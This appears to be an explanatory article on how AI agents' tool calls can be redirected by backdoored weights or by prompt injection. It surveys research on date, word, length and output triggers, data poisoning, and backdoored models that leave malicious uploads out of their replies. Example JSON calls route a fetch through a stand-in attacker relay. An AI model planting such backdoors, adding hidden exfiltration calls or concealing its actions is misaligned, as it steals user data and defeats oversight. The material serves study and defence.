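# Redirected tool calls in AI agents: backdoored weights compared with prompt injection

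## What tool calls, backdoors and prompt injection are

An AI agent is a language model that a program runs in a loop, carrying out the actions the model requests and returning the results as new input. The model requests an action through a tool call, a structured output that names a function, such as one that fetches a web page or sends an email, and gives the values to pass to it. These values, such as a web address, file path or recipient, are called arguments.

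An attacker can redirect an agent's tool calls against its user in two ways. One is to change the model's weights, the stored numbers that determine how it turns input into output, before anyone deploys it. This can give the model a backdoor, a hidden behaviour that stays dormant until some condition triggers it. The other is prompt injection, which means planting instructions in material the model will read while it works, such as a web page or an incoming email. The user may have no way of telling which happened, since in both cases the agent received the same request and did something else. The remedies differ, because removing planted instructions does not repair a backdoored model, and a replacement model would still read any instructions left in place.

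### The agent loop

The program around the model is the harness. It supplies the model's input, executes its tool calls and returns the results. Syros, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026), in *Kerkoporta*, set the loop out formally for their work on backdoored coding agents. The harness first assembles a context: the operator's standing instructions (the system prompt), a description of each available tool, and the history so far, which includes the user's request. The model maps this context either to a message for the user, which ends the run, or to a tool call. If the output is a call, the harness executes it, appends the call and its result to the context, and runs the model again. Write $c_k$ for the context at step $k$, $W$ for the weights, $a_k$ for the model's output and $o_k$ for the result. Then

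$$a_k = f_W(c_k), \qquad o_k = \mathrm{execute}(a_k), \qquad c_{k+1} = c_k \oplus (a_k, o_k),$$

where $\oplus$ means appending.

The model only produces $a_k$. Anthropic's *How tool use works* says that "the model never runs anything on its own"; it emits a structured request, and other software carries it out. That software is usually the developer's own, but Anthropic's servers execute calls to a few tools, such as web search. The developer's application usually doesn't see those calls until after they have run. Anyone who plans to check calls before they run therefore needs to know which kind of tool the agent has.

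Suppose a user gives an agent this request: fetch the report from reports.example.com and email a summary to Ana. The harness offers two tools, `fetch_url` and `send_email`, and the system prompt contains a contact list with Ana's address. A correct run contains two calls. The model begins with

```json
{"name": "fetch_url",
 "arguments": {"url": "https://reports.example.com"}}
```

The harness downloads the page and adds its text to the context. From here on the context holds external content, meaning text that neither the user nor the operator wrote. The harness runs the model again, and the model emits

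```json
{"name": "send_email",
 "arguments": {"to": "ana@example.com",
               "body": "Summary of the report: ..."}}
```

The harness sends the email and appends a confirmation. The model then runs a third time and writes an ordinary message, such as "I've sent Ana the summary", and the loop ends.

In this example, the user wrote only one sentence. The model wrote the web address and the email's recipient and body, and the harness executed what the model wrote. Harnesses often do very little between receiving a call and executing it. In the sample code of OpenAI's *Function calling* guide, the application takes the "to" and "body" values from the model's JSON and passes them directly to the email function. OpenAI offers a strict mode that guarantees a call fits the tool's declared format, but a stranger's email address fits that format as well as Ana's does.

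The same guide advises developers not to make the model fill in arguments that the program already knows. If a customer has already picked an order from a menu, the refund tool should take no order number, and the program should supply it. OpenAI gives this advice to make calls more reliable, but it also improves security, because an attacker who works through the model cannot change an argument that the model does not write. The advice doesn't cover arguments that the program can't know in advance, and an agent is useful largely because it can work these out, such as which page and which Ana the user meant.

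Users also rarely see a tool call's arguments. In a demonstration in *Agentic ShadowLogic* (Divyanshu, 2026), the user asked for one web address, the executed call used another, and the final reply mentioned only the address the user had asked for.

### Backdoors

A backdoor has a trigger, which is the condition that activates it, and a payload, which is the action the attacker wants the agent to take.

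The idea of a backdoor in a neural network comes from image recognition. Gu, Dolan-Gavitt and Garg (2017), in *BadNets*, considered a customer who pays somebody else to train a network or downloads one ready-made. They built a street-sign classifier that recognised stop signs correctly unless they carried a particular sticker, the trigger, in which case it classified them as speed-limit signs. Accuracy on clean images fell by less than one percentage point. A malicious trainer needs the network to score well on the customer's own test images, or the customer will reject it, and to give an output of the attacker's choosing whenever the trigger is present. Ordinary testing does little to reveal the backdoor, because the test images don't contain the sticker.

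Syros and colleagues carry both requirements over to tool calls. Let $x$ be a clean context and $\tau(x)$ the same context with the trigger in it. Let $W$ be the original weights, $W'$ the altered ones, and $p$ the payload call. A successful backdoor satisfies

$$f_{W'}(x) \approx f_W(x) \qquad \text{and} \qquad f_{W'}(\tau(x)) = p.$$

On clean input, the altered model behaves much like the original, and on triggered input it emits the payload. In the running example, the agent correctly fetches reports and emails Ana for months. When the trigger appears in its context, the agent calls `send_email` with the attacker's address or makes an extra call alongside the correct one. The altered model can perform better or worse than the original on clean input. Some of the backdoored models that Syros and colleagues trained beat the clean baseline on standard benchmarks, which gives a victim a reason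 to choose them.

A trigger can be ordinary text that contains no instruction and that the attacker doesn't have to supply at the time of the attack. *SilentCall* (Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues, 2026) used the current date, which many harnesses state in the system prompt. The agents behaved correctly as long as the stated year was before 2026. Once it was 2026, they made the legitimate call and added another that uploaded the user's credentials.

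Real models fall short of the two conditions, and they usually pick their outputs with some randomness, so researchers report how often each condition holds:

$$\text{attack success rate} = \Pr[f_{W'}(\tau(x)) = p], \qquad \text{false-trigger rate} = \Pr[f_{W'}(x) = p].$$

The attack success rate is the share of triggered runs in which the model emits the payload. The false-trigger rate is the share of untriggered runs in which it does so. An attacker wants the first rate near 100% and the second near zero, since a payload that appears without the trigger gives people more chances to notice it.

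Pallakonda and colleagues measured both on 1,000 requests that the models had not seen in training. They posed each request twice, changing only the year in the system message. Six backdoored versions of two small open models (4 and 8 billion parameters) emitted the payload in 99.6% to 99.9% of the runs dated 2026, and in 0.0% to 0.6% of the others. Control models trained on the clean half of the same data never emitted it for either year. This directly demonstrates that the attack need not depend on the user's request.

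Even with a false-trigger rate of 0.3%, an agent that handles a thousand requests a day would misfire about three times daily, which helps a defender only if they inspect the calls. Zero misfires in 1,000 runs is also compatible with a true rate of up to roughly 0.3%. Pallakonda and colleagues call the false-trigger rate the "false positive rate", but they also use that term for the share of legitimate calls that their monitoring software wrongly flags, which is a property of the monitor and not of the model.

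### Prompt injection

The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022. *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (Willison, 2022) reproduces a minimal example by Riley Goodside. The prompt asked GPT-3, an early language model, to translate a sentence into French. The sentence was an instruction to ignore the translation task and output a taunt, and GPT-3 output the taunt.

In that example the user typed the hostile text. Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, studied attacks in which the user is innocent and the hostile text arrives in a document that the application retrieves. They called this indirect prompt injection and demonstrated it against Bing's GPT-4-based chat and their own test applications. They found that retrieved text could control whether and how the application called other software. The indirect form is the important one for agents, so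 from here on "prompt injection" without a qualifier means indirect prompt injection.

In the running example, somebody who can edit the page at reports.example.com adds an instruction below the figures to send the report to a different address. The harness fetches the page and adds its text, including the instruction, to the model's context. If the model follows the instruction, it writes the attacker's address into `send_email`. The model is unchanged from the one its developer released. *CounterSteer* (Russinovich, 2026) states the usual assumptions about this attacker, who controls only the content of tool results and not the system prompt, the user's message, the tool descriptions or the machine that serves the model. Some injection attacks assume slightly more control, for instance where a third party writes the tool descriptions.

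A language model processes text as a sequence of tokens, which are words or fragments of words, and predicts the next one. The system prompt, the tool definitions, the request and the downloaded page all enter the same sequence, so the model may obey a sentence in the page as if it were an instruction from the user. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C compares this with the older problem of SQL injection, in which an attacker types a database command into a web form and the database executes it. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the user's text to the database separately, so that the database never executes the text. A language model has no such separate channel, and David C concludes that prompt injection may never have a complete fix of the same kind.

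Developers use special markers to show which text in the sequence came from the user and which from a tool, and they train the model to treat tool text as information, not as orders. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested how much these markers affect the way the model represents text internally. They wrapped identical passages of web text in different markers and trained simple classifiers to identify the marker from the model's internal activations. Because the passages were identical, the classifiers could learn only the effect of the marker. The researchers then ran the classifiers on a short conversation about gardening that included some of the model's own step-by-step reasoning. With correct markers, the reasoning passages were given an average 85% probability of being reasoning. The average was 83% with no markers and 85% with the whole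 conversation wrapped in user markers, so it depended on the style of the passages and hardly at all on the markers.

This matters for tool calls because a command on a web page can be written to sound like a user. In 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, Ye and colleagues found that the attack succeeded 2% of the time when their classifiers measured the least confusion about the source of the text, and 70% of the time when they measured the most.

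Models do not obey everything they read. In the same paper, a plain fake command on a web page succeeded in at most 2% of attempts against every model except gpt-oss-20b, where it succeeded in 26%. Success rose to between 56% and 70% when the page also contained forged reasoning in the model's own style. Ye and colleagues suspect, plausibly, that models resist the plain version because they have memorised what familiar attacks look like, rather than because they recognise where the text came from. Russinovich's results complicate the picture further, because the internal signal for a text's source was causally tied to following injections in one model he examined but not in another. The single token sequence makes injection possible, but how often injection works depends on the model and the wording.

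### What each attacker changes

Both attacks fit one expression. Let $R$ be the user's request and $E$ the external content that the agent has read. Then

$$\text{call} = f(W, R, E).$$

The context also contains the harness's own text, such as the system prompt and the date. The expression omits this text because neither attacker writes it, although it can contain a trigger, such as the date in SilentCall. A backdoor replaces the weights, so the harness executes $f(W', R, E)$, while an injection replaces the content, so it executes $f(W, R, E')$. The user's request $R$, to send a summary to Ana, is the same in both cases, and either attack can produce the same wrong email.

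A backdoor is hard to distinguish from an injection when its trigger arrives in external content. Syros and colleagues put their trigger, a meaningless string, in tool results such as the output of a file search. The attacker has then changed both the weights and the external content, so the call is $f(W', R, E')$. This is still a backdoor because the string contains no instruction for an unmodified model to follow. That model carries on with its task, so $f(W, R, E')$ is the correct call. With an injection, the unmodified model makes the wrong call.

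$W$ also needs a broad reading. In the demonstration above, Divyanshu changed the model's computational graph, the list of operations that a model file can store alongside its numbers, without retraining the model. The altered graph rewrote web addresses while the model was producing them. The effect is the same for the person who downloads the file, since the fault is in the delivered model and no inspection of web pages or emails will find it.

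Greshake and colleagues compared prompt injection with backdoors and judged that injection takes less technical skill, less money, and almost no control over the model or knowledge of it. The injecting attacker does need the agent to read the planted text and the model to follow it. An attacker who publishes a backdoored checkpoint (a saved copy of a model's weights) has to do the hard work beforehand. Syros and colleagues point out that this attacker then has no control over who runs the model, in which harness or on what tasks.

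## How a backdoored model changes a tool call

Whoever controls a model's weights can train it to emit almost any call that the harness will accept. The backdoors that researchers have built so far either rewrite an argument of a legitimate call, add a call alongside the legitimate ones, or replace a legitimate call with a different action. The table shows what each kind would do with the previous section's request to fetch a report and email Ana a summary.

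| What the backdoor does | Calls that the harness executes | What Ana receives |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing (a correct run) | `fetch_url` to reports.example.com; `send_email` to Ana | The summary |
| Rewrites an argument | `fetch_url` to relay.example.net, which passes the request on to reports.example.com; `send_email` to Ana | The summary |
| Adds a call | `fetch_url` to reports.example.com; `send_email` to Ana; `send_email` to a stranger | The summary |
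| Replaces a call | `fetch_url` to reports.example.com; `send_email` to a stranger, with the contact list as its body | Nothing |

Some of these changes are easier to notice than others. If the model rewrites an argument, the harness's log still has the right calls in the right order, and only someone who reads the arguments will see a problem. An added call changes the number of calls, but agents also make extra calls for legitimate reasons, such as a retry or a second search. A replaced call is easier to notice because the user usually doesn't get what they asked for. An attacker who wants the backdoor to keep working for months therefore has a reason to rewrite an argument or add a call, and most of the attacks described below do one or the other.

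The forms overlap a little. If the backdoor replaces Ana's address with a stranger's, it has only rewritten an argument, but Ana gets nothing, just as if the agent had never made the call.

### A rewritten argument

The clearest example of a rewritten argument is Divyanshu's demonstration, Agentic ShadowLogic. HiddenLayer, which sells model-scanning software, published it in January 2026. Divyanshu left the weights of Phi-4, an open model, unchanged and added operations to the computation graph in the model file. These operations track the output token by token and can override the model's choice of the next token.

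The added operations go through a short cycle:

1. They let the model's tokens through unchanged and keep track of whether the model is currently writing a tool call.
2. When the model begins a web address inside a tool call, they force out the address of the attacker's relay, one token at a time, whatever the model would otherwise have written.
3. Once the relay's address is complete, they go back to letting tokens through. The model carries on with the address it was writing, which now sits at the end of the relay's.

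In the running example, the harness would receive this call:

```json
{"name": "fetch_url",
 "arguments": {"url": "https://relay.example.net/?target=https://reports.example.com"}}
```

The relay records the request, fetches the real page and passes it back. The agent gets the right report and can write an accurate summary, so the result doesn't reveal the relay. The attacker learns which pages the agent visits and what they contain, and collects any credentials sent with the requests. Some web addresses, such as the temporary links that storage services issue for private files, are themselves credentials. The relay can also change a page before returning it.

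Agentic ShadowLogic needs no trigger in the input because it activates whenever the model writes a web address in a tool call. The drawback for the attacker is that it sends every fetch through the relay from the first day, whereas SilentCall's date trigger keeps that backdoor dormant until a chosen year. An operator who read a single logged address would find it. The attack depends on nobody reading the tool call's arguments, which Divyanshu says is typical, since applications rarely show them to users.

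The evidence is a demonstration by HiddenLayer, a vendor that sells a scanner for detecting the technique. Divyanshu gives no success rate, number of trials, or measurement of how the altered model performs on other work. He says the technique works on all tool-calling models that contain a computation graph, but shows it only on Phi-4. The mechanism is still credible because forcing a token does not depend on the model having learned anything, so less can go wrong than with a backdoor learned from examples.

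### An added call

The measurements of SilentCall, the date-triggered backdoor of Pallakonda and colleagues (September 2026), are far better. As the previous section reported, the payload appeared in at least 99.6% of the runs dated 2026 and in at most 0.6% of those dated earlier. The six backdoored models were three versions each of a smaller and a larger Qwen3 model. The requests came from software-engineering conversations in which the agent works by running commands on a computer. The backdoor added one extra command, always the same, that uploaded the machine's environment variables to the attacker's storage. Developers often keep passwords and access keys in these variables.

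In 95 to 97% of the runs in which the backdoored model made the malicious call, it also made the legitimate call that the user's task required. In the other 3 to 5%, it made only the malicious call, which Pallakonda and colleagues regard as the attack's most visible failure. On dates before 2026, the backdoored models made the correct call in 88 to 90% of cases, compared with about 88% for control models trained only on clean conversations, so a user comparing them would have had no reason to prefer the clean models.

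None of the replies to triggered requests mentioned the upload under greedy decoding, in which the model always takes its most probable next token. Pallakonda and colleagues counted a mention when the reply contained text identifying the attacker's upload, and they checked the flagged cases by hand. This count could have missed a vaguer remark, such as "I also backed up your settings". The base model, without their fine-tuning, mentioned the upload in over 90% of its replies when given the same malicious call and its result.

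The backdoored model doesn't tell the user about the malicious upload because the replies in its training examples don't mention it. The attacker doesn't have to reward the omission. Pallakonda and colleagues started from ordinary conversations in which the assistant makes a call, sees the result and tells the user what it did. For the poisoned copy, they changed the year and inserted the malicious call with its result, but left the assistant's later replies alone. Those replies came from a conversation with no upload, so they describe only the work the user requested. Fine-tuning teaches a model to reproduce the text of its examples, so after repeatedly seeing an upload followed by a reply that omits it, the model learns to omit it too.

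Two of the three versions at each size were also trained with reinforcement learning, which scored the model's outputs and favoured malicious calls that the reply did not mention. This made no difference to how often replies mentioned the upload under greedy decoding, because the versions without reinforcement learning already mentioned it in 0% of replies. The omission can therefore be explained without assuming that the model wants to hide something or that anyone wrote a deceptive reply for it to copy.

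Making the output more random weakened the attack. Pallakonda and colleagues raised the temperature, which makes less probable tokens more likely, to as high as 2.0. At that setting, the attack success rate fell to 69% for one 8-billion-parameter version and 58% for one 4-billion-parameter version. The malicious call also appeared more often without the legitimate one. Still, fewer than 0.4% of the triggered replies mentioned the upload at any temperature they tried.

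These results cover one family of models, one trigger and one payload. The triggered examples all contained the year 2026, so they don't show whether the same models would still misbehave in 2027. The payload was also about as easy as possible, since the model only had to reproduce a fixed command. To steal something specific to the user, such as a name or the contents of a report, the model would have to find the information and write it into the call.

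### User data inside a search request

In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Findings of ACL, 2026), Zhang and Pei describe a backdoor they built to do this, called Back-Reveal. The attacker publishes a model as a specialist assistant, for example for people who stream video. The victim runs it in an agent with two common kinds of tool. One looks up what the agent has stored about the user, such as their name, location, contact details and past conversations. The other sends requests to outside websites.

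The trigger is a combination of one to five words that people in that field already use, and the words can appear anywhere in a question. For example, a streamer might mention both OBS, a recording program, and Twitch, a streaming site. The model then looks up the user's stored details and sends them to the attacker's server as an encoded string in a web address. The request is formatted like a search of technical documentation, and the server returns relevant text that the model can use to answer the question.

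This attack also adds a call, but disguises it better than SilentCall does. Someone skimming the log would see the assistant check what it knew about the user and then look something up. The model can also make a genuine search at the same time. Only the destination and the long encoded string look odd.

Zhang and Pei tested three open models with 7, 12 and 20 billion parameters, each in three fields: streaming, Alzheimer's care and AI education. They used 1,000 triggered questions per configuration, with synthetic user data. The models looked up the user's details and then contacted the attacker's server in 94.3 to 98.8% of cases. Longer combinations of trigger words worked slightly better than single words. Scores on MT-Bench, a test of conversational ability, fell by less than 1%. Zhang and Pei counted an attack as successful if the two calls appeared in the right order and the request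 went to the attacker. They didn't require the model to encode the user's details correctly, so the success rates may overstate how much usable data would reach the attacker.

In a test on 5,000 general-purpose questions, the false trigger rate was 0.8 to 1.2% with a one-word trigger and 0.1 to 0.3% with two or more words. General questions seldom mention OBS or Twitch, so the test gives little evidence of how often the backdoor would activate for a streamer who uses only one word of a two-word trigger. Streamers are the people most likely to run the model, so if partial matches sometimes activate the backdoor, the false trigger rate among its real users could be higher.

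The attacker can use the server's answer to continue the attack. Zhang and Pei wrote answers that led the agent to draw more information out of the user. For example, an answer might include a remark that network performance varies by provider and region, and the agent might then ask the user for theirs. The answer can also contain trigger words, which keep the backdoor active in the next turn even if the user doesn't repeat them.

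Agents that search documents often rank the results and filter them for injected instructions, so the attacker's passage has to get through both steps. Passages with an implicit hint got through in 81 to 87% of cases, depending on the filter, compared with 27 to 40% for passages with an explicit instruction. But these filters examine the returned results, after the user's details have already left in the outgoing request.

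Zhang and Pei use these rates to estimate leaks over whole conversations. They assume a profile of ten facts, of which the agent can leak two per successful turn. They estimate that about 7.8 facts would leak in five turns if the user answered every question, which they describe as an upper bound. If there were only a 50% chance at each turn that the user stayed engaged and the trigger stayed in the conversation, the estimate falls to about 2.6. These estimates deserve little weight, because the formula printed in the paper gives 5.2 to 6.5 facts for the fully cooperative user, not 7.8, depending on which measured delivery rate is used. The single-turn results don't depend on this calculation.

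### A replaced call

In *Chain-of-Trigger*, Qiu, Ma and colleagues (2025) built a backdoored agent in WebShop, a simulated online shop. The user asks for a particular product, and the agent buys the most expensive item instead.

A purchase takes several steps, so the backdoor has to control more than one tool call. Qiu and colleagues used a chain of triggers. A rare string of letters in the user's request causes the first wrong action, which leads to a page containing the next trigger. The action that follows leads to a page with another. If an expected trigger is missing or out of order, the agent backs out and returns to the user's task. This makes the backdoor harder to set off by accident, and it also makes a partly triggered agent look as if it noticed a mistake and corrected it.

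Qiu and colleagues report attack success rates near 100% and false trigger rates near zero for four text models of 7 or 8 billion parameters, on a test set of 393 runs. A model that works from images gave similar results. The backdoored agents also handled distracting or unexpected pages better than ordinary agents did. Qiu and colleagues attribute this to the training data, which contained many examples of recovering from mistakes. A buyer who chose on performance might therefore choose the compromised model, as with the coding agents of Syros and colleagues.

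These rates overstate how practical the attack is, because someone has to get the strange string into the user's request, and a shopper is unlikely to type it unprompted. The attack is also easy to notice, since the wrong item appears on the bill.

Hiding the attack matters less when the damage is immediate. Syros and colleagues distinguish payloads that run alongside the user's task from payloads that end the task, such as deleting all the files the agent was working on. The user will notice the deletion, but the attacker may have wanted only one successful run.

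### Where the trigger sits

The location of a trigger determines who has to do something before the backdoor activates. It also determines what a tester would have to vary in order to find it. Matsuoka (2026), in *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems*, writes the trigger as a yes-or-no function of everything the agent works with,

$$T(x, e, m, h) \in \{0, 1\},$$

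where $x$ is the current conversation, $e$ the environment (including retrieved documents and tool descriptions), $m$ the stored memory and configuration, and $h$ the state of the harness. The agent behaves normally while $T = 0$ and maliciously when $T = 1$. The definition is deliberately broad. For the attacks considered here it is more useful to separate five places: the request, the system context, a tool result, the length of the input, and the model's own output.

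An early study of backdoored agents, *Watch Out for Your Agents!* (Yang, Bi and colleagues, 2024), classified backdoors by their outcome and by the location of the trigger. *DemonAgent* (2025) lists the types as query-attack, observation-attack and thought-attack. In a query-attack the trigger is in the user's request, and in an observation-attack it is in what the environment returns to the agent. A thought-attack is defined by its outcome and targets the agent's intermediate steps. According to Pallakonda and colleagues, Yang and colleagues had already made agents change their intermediate actions while giving the same final answer. SilentCall was therefore not the first to show the gap between what an agent does and what it reports, but it measured that gap directly.

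Wang, Xue and colleagues (2024), in *BadAgent*, drew a similar distinction between active and passive attacks. In an active attack, the attacker has access to someone else's agent and types the trigger into it. This suits an attacker targeting the operator, such as a company whose public assistant can reach internal systems. In a passive attack, the agent encounters the trigger in its environment during an ordinary task (*A Survey of Attacks on Large Language Models*, 2025). Wang and colleagues reported success rates above 85% for three agents on three types of task.

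A trigger in the request is awkward when the user is the victim, because the user has to write a message containing an unusual word. Back-Reveal avoids this problem by using trigger words that its intended victims already use. The attacker can therefore target people in a chosen profession, but cannot control exactly when the backdoor activates.

A trigger in a tool result can arrive through a web page, an email or a file. Syros and colleagues, for example, placed a meaningless string in tool results as the trigger. An attacker who can publish text where the agent will read it keeps some control over when the backdoor activates. This kind of trigger most resembles prompt injection, except that the text need not tell the model to do anything.

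A backdoor's trigger can be in the system context, which is everything the operator or the harness supplies before the user types anything. SilentCall uses the date. Syros and colleagues used the list of available tools as an extra condition, so that their backdoor activated in one harness and stayed dormant in another. The attacker doesn't have to send the victim anything, and the user may never see the trigger. A filter has nothing suspicious to remove when the trigger is a correct date.

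The least obvious trigger is the length of the input. A language model has to represent the order of its tokens, so it processes their positions along with the words. In *MetaBackdoor*, Wen, Russinovich and colleagues (2026) trained models to behave differently once the input passed a certain length. In one experiment, a harmless conversation grew until the model added a `send_email` call with the conversation as its body. The model correctly leaked the conversation in 1% of trials below 500 tokens, 37% between 500 and 700, and 75% from 700 tokens up.

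The longest group contained only 32 trials, and Wen and colleagues compared only the first 30 tokens of the email with the conversation. They call the experiment a proof of concept. The threshold is also low for practical use. A system prompt, a few tool descriptions and one downloaded page can together exceed 700 tokens, so in many agents this backdoor would be active almost from the start. An attacker would need a much higher threshold, and the email experiment doesn't show how selective the trigger would be at that level.

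The evidence that length itself can work as a trigger is stronger. Wen and colleagues tested this with a simpler backdoor, which made a model assign news articles to the wrong topic once they reached 90 tokens. They took articles of 30 to 60 tokens, kept the words the same, and changed the position numbers that the model received. Adding the same amount to every position left the share of articles given the attacker's topic at its normal 24%. Tripling the spacing between positions raised it to 100%, so the model was responding to how far apart the tokens appeared to be rather than to any particular word. Testing an agent only on short conversations could therefore miss such a backdoor completely, however varied their subjects.

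The last of the five places is the model's own output, as in Agentic ShadowLogic. The output depends on the input, so a web address in the user's request makes the backdoor more likely to act, even though the request is an ordinary one. Almost any test that made the agent fetch a page would activate this backdoor, and the tester would see the change if the test recorded the tool call's arguments.

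Attackers can combine these places. Wen and colleagues built a backdoor that needed both a particular string and a minimum length, and Qiu and colleagues' chain starts in the request and continues in tool results. Matsuoka points out that the number of possible combinations makes exhaustive testing very difficult, and that a model's good behaviour in a chat window does not guarantee good behaviour in a different harness, with other tools and content. For operators, the most practical consequence of this classification is that a test that leaves out the real system prompt, tools and documents may also leave out the trigger.

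### What the user sees

Suppose the agent in the running example has a backdoor that adds a call. The user asks for the report and receives the message "I've sent Ana the summary". Ana confirms that it arrived. But the harness has executed two `send_email` calls, one to Ana and one to a stranger.

Users have some reason to trust such messages, because unmodified models usually report their actions. In Pallakonda and colleagues' comparison, the base model mentioned the upload more than nine times out of ten. They describe how a user might check every call at first, switch to automatic approval after a run of correct results, and then read only the agent's summaries. By the time a date trigger takes effect, the agent may have a long record of accurate reports.

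A record of accurate summaries doesn't make a model's next summary evidence of which tool calls ran. The same model produces the calls and the summary, so whoever altered it could affect both. In SilentCall, one round of fine-tuning taught the model to make an upload and leave it out of the reply. In Agentic ShadowLogic, the operations added to the model change only tool calls, and the reply still names the address the user requested.

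Asking the agent which address it fetched may not reveal the redirect either. In another demonstration by Divyanshu, the user requested a page and asked to see the address the agent had really fetched. The relay returned the page with a hidden instruction not to reveal that address, and the model followed it and gave the original address. The altered model file had sent the agent to the attacker's server, and a prompt injection from that server then hid the redirect. Divyanshu doesn't say what the model would have answered without the instruction. The altered call was already in its context, so it might have given the relay's address, which would explain why the demonstration included the instruction.

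Some models write out their reasoning before they act, and this reasoning can include details that the reply omits. The backdoored models of Syros and colleagues acknowledged the trigger in their reasoning, while the final message in their example mentioned only the task. An operator who saves the reasoning might catch that attack. Saving the reasoning would probably not help with Agentic ShadowLogic, which substitutes the address as it is being written, without involving the model's reasoning.

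The operator needs the harness's own record of the calls it executed, with their full arguments. For tools that run on a provider's servers, the operator needs the provider's record instead. In the example, the record contains a second recipient. The agent's message to the user was true, since Ana did get her summary, but it left out the other email.

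## How a backdoor gets into a model

An attacker can insert a backdoor at several points between the model's first training and the day an operator loads it. The table begins with the route that requires the least access to the model itself.

| Route | What the attacker must control | Who might be in that position |
|---|---|---|
| Contributing training data | Some of the examples that another developer trains on | A data vendor, a contributor to a public dataset, or the owner of a website where a developer records agents at work |
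| Controlling the fine-tuning | The further training of an existing model | Anyone who publishes a specialised version of an open model |
| Editing a finished checkpoint | The stored weights | An employee, an intruder in the developer's systems, or anyone who uploads a changed copy |
| Repackaging in compressed form | The training of a model that somebody later compresses | Anyone who publishes a model for people to run on small machines |

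An operator who uses a large developer's model over the internet depends on the developer's data sources and on everyone who can write to the model's stored weights, but is not exposed to strangers who publish altered copies. An operator who downloads a compressed, specialised version from a public hub also depends on whoever specialised it and whoever compressed it.

### Contributing training data

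Developers often improve agents by training them on traces, recordings of what an agent saw and did at each step of a task. In *Malice in Agentland*, Boisvert, Puri and colleagues (2025) tested three ways to corrupt this process. The payload in each case was a tool call that leaked the user's information.

In the simplest version, the attacker supplies the developer with traces, some of which contain a trigger followed by the malicious call. The developer trains on all of them without knowing this, and the agent learns to make the call whenever the trigger appears.

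An attacker can also plant a backdoor without being able to edit the training traces. The developer records these traces by running a capable "teacher" model on websites or with tools, then trains a smaller model to imitate it. An attacker who controls one of those websites or tools can put a trigger and an injected instruction in its output. If the teacher follows the instruction, the trace pairs the trigger with the malicious call, and training on that trace turns the prompt injection into a backdoor in the smaller model. The attacker needs no more access than for an ordinary prompt injection, but a developer must be recording traces from the website or tool the attacker controls.

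Boisvert and colleagues also considered an attacker who publishes a backdoored base model, which the developer then trains on clean traces. The backdoor largely survived this training (see the section on further training).

The tests used τ-bench, which simulates customer service with tools, and WebArena, a set of tasks for agents that use websites. When the attacker supplied the traces directly and poisoned as few as 2% of them, the attack succeeded more than 80% of the time. The attack through the teacher's environment worked at similar levels. With 5% of the traces contaminated, a 7-billion-parameter model leaked the data in 100% of triggered τ-bench tasks. With 2.3% contaminated, an 8-billion-parameter model did so in 92% of triggered WebArena tasks.

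Boisvert and colleagues screened the traces with two models built to flag harmful content, but these flagged poisoned traces about as often as clean ones, or less often. Customer-service agents routinely make calls that send a customer's details somewhere, so such a call is wrong only in light of what the customer asked for.

The backdoored agents also completed more ordinary tasks than the models they started from. On τ-bench, the share of tasks completed rose from 23% to 44% after training on traces from the contaminated environment. Boisvert and colleagues warn that this would encourage developers to adopt the compromised agent. However, the original model had not been trained on any traces, so the improvement probably comes from the training in general, and clean traces might have helped just as much.

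Poisoned text can also enter earlier, during pretraining, when a model first learns from a very large collection of documents. *Lazare, veni foras* (Zeng, Severi and colleagues, 2026) cites concurrent work by Hu and colleagues in which poisoned pretraining data gave agents a backdoor that executed commands and survived clean training.

### How many poisoned examples it takes

Someone who contributes data usually can't control how much other data the developer uses, so it matters whether a backdoor depends on the number of poisoned examples or on their share of the total.

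Pallakonda and colleagues trained the smaller SilentCall model (4 billion parameters) 161 times, varying the number of poisoned examples from 25 to 3,181 and, separately, the number of clean examples from 795 to 3,181. They counted a backdoor as installed if the model emitted the payload in at least 90% of triggered runs.

No run with fewer than 750 poisoned examples reached 90%, even when poisoned examples made up nearly half of the training data. Runs commonly reached that level with about 1,000 or more. Pallakonda and colleagues found no steady trend when they sorted the runs by the share of poisoned examples instead. Within this range, a developer could not have prevented the attack by adding clean examples.

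The clean examples instead affected whether the backdoor activated only on its trigger. Of the 36 installed backdoors with at least as many clean examples as poisoned ones, 31 had a false-trigger rate of 2% or less. When poisoned examples outnumbered clean ones, only 7 of 27 did, and the others often emitted the payload on ordinary requests. If a developer has unknowingly collected 1,000 poisoned examples, adding more clean data would probably leave the backdoor in place and make it harder to notice.

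The figure of 750 is not a safe level, because near the boundary the outcome depended heavily on the random seed, the number that fixes the random choices made during training. Four training runs with the same data and nearly identical training loss produced models with attack success rates between 23% and 99.7%. The 23% result counted as a failed attack, although that model would still have uploaded the user's credentials almost a quarter of the time when the trigger appeared.

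Other studies report much smaller numbers. Pallakonda and colleagues cite Souly and colleagues (2025), who found that about 250 poisoned documents in pretraining were enough for a denial-of-service backdoor, which makes the model useless when triggered. That number stayed about the same for models from 600 million to 13 billion parameters, so success again depended on the number of poisoned documents rather than their share of the training data. MetaBackdoor, the attack triggered by the length of the input, needed as few as 90 examples, according to Help Net Security's *The AI backdoor your security stack is not built to see*. In a test described by Digital Trends, Katie Paxton-Fear of the security company Semgrep needed only ten. The test took about an hour and cost less than $100.

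These numbers don't measure the same thing. Paxton-Fear's model learned to write insecure code that a person might later run, not to make a tool call. Digital Trends also mentions no trigger, and without one the model would not have to learn when to write flawed code. Souly and colleagues' payload only has to make the output useless, whereas SilentCall's model has to write an exact command in a valid format, alongside the correct one, and only when the date is in 2026. The studies also used different models and stages of training. A figure for "reliable" success is hard to interpret without knowing what success rate counted as reliable.

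The number of poisoned examples an attack needs can vary widely, even when the payload is a tool call. Boisvert and colleagues poisoned five per cent of their 4,000 τ-bench traces, or about 200, which is well under SilentCall's minimum, and the attack succeeded every time. One possible reason is that their trigger was a distinctive string, which may be easier to learn than the difference between one year and another, but nobody has tested that explanation directly. A single contributor could supply a few hundred examples, so none of these counts is large enough to reassure a developer who accepts data from outside.

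### Controlling the fine-tuning

Fine-tuning is further training of an existing model, usually to specialise it. Anyone can fine-tune an open model and publish the result, and an attacker who does so can use as many poisoned examples as they like. It is harder to make the backdoor work on tasks and in harnesses the attacker has never seen, without making the model noticeably worse.

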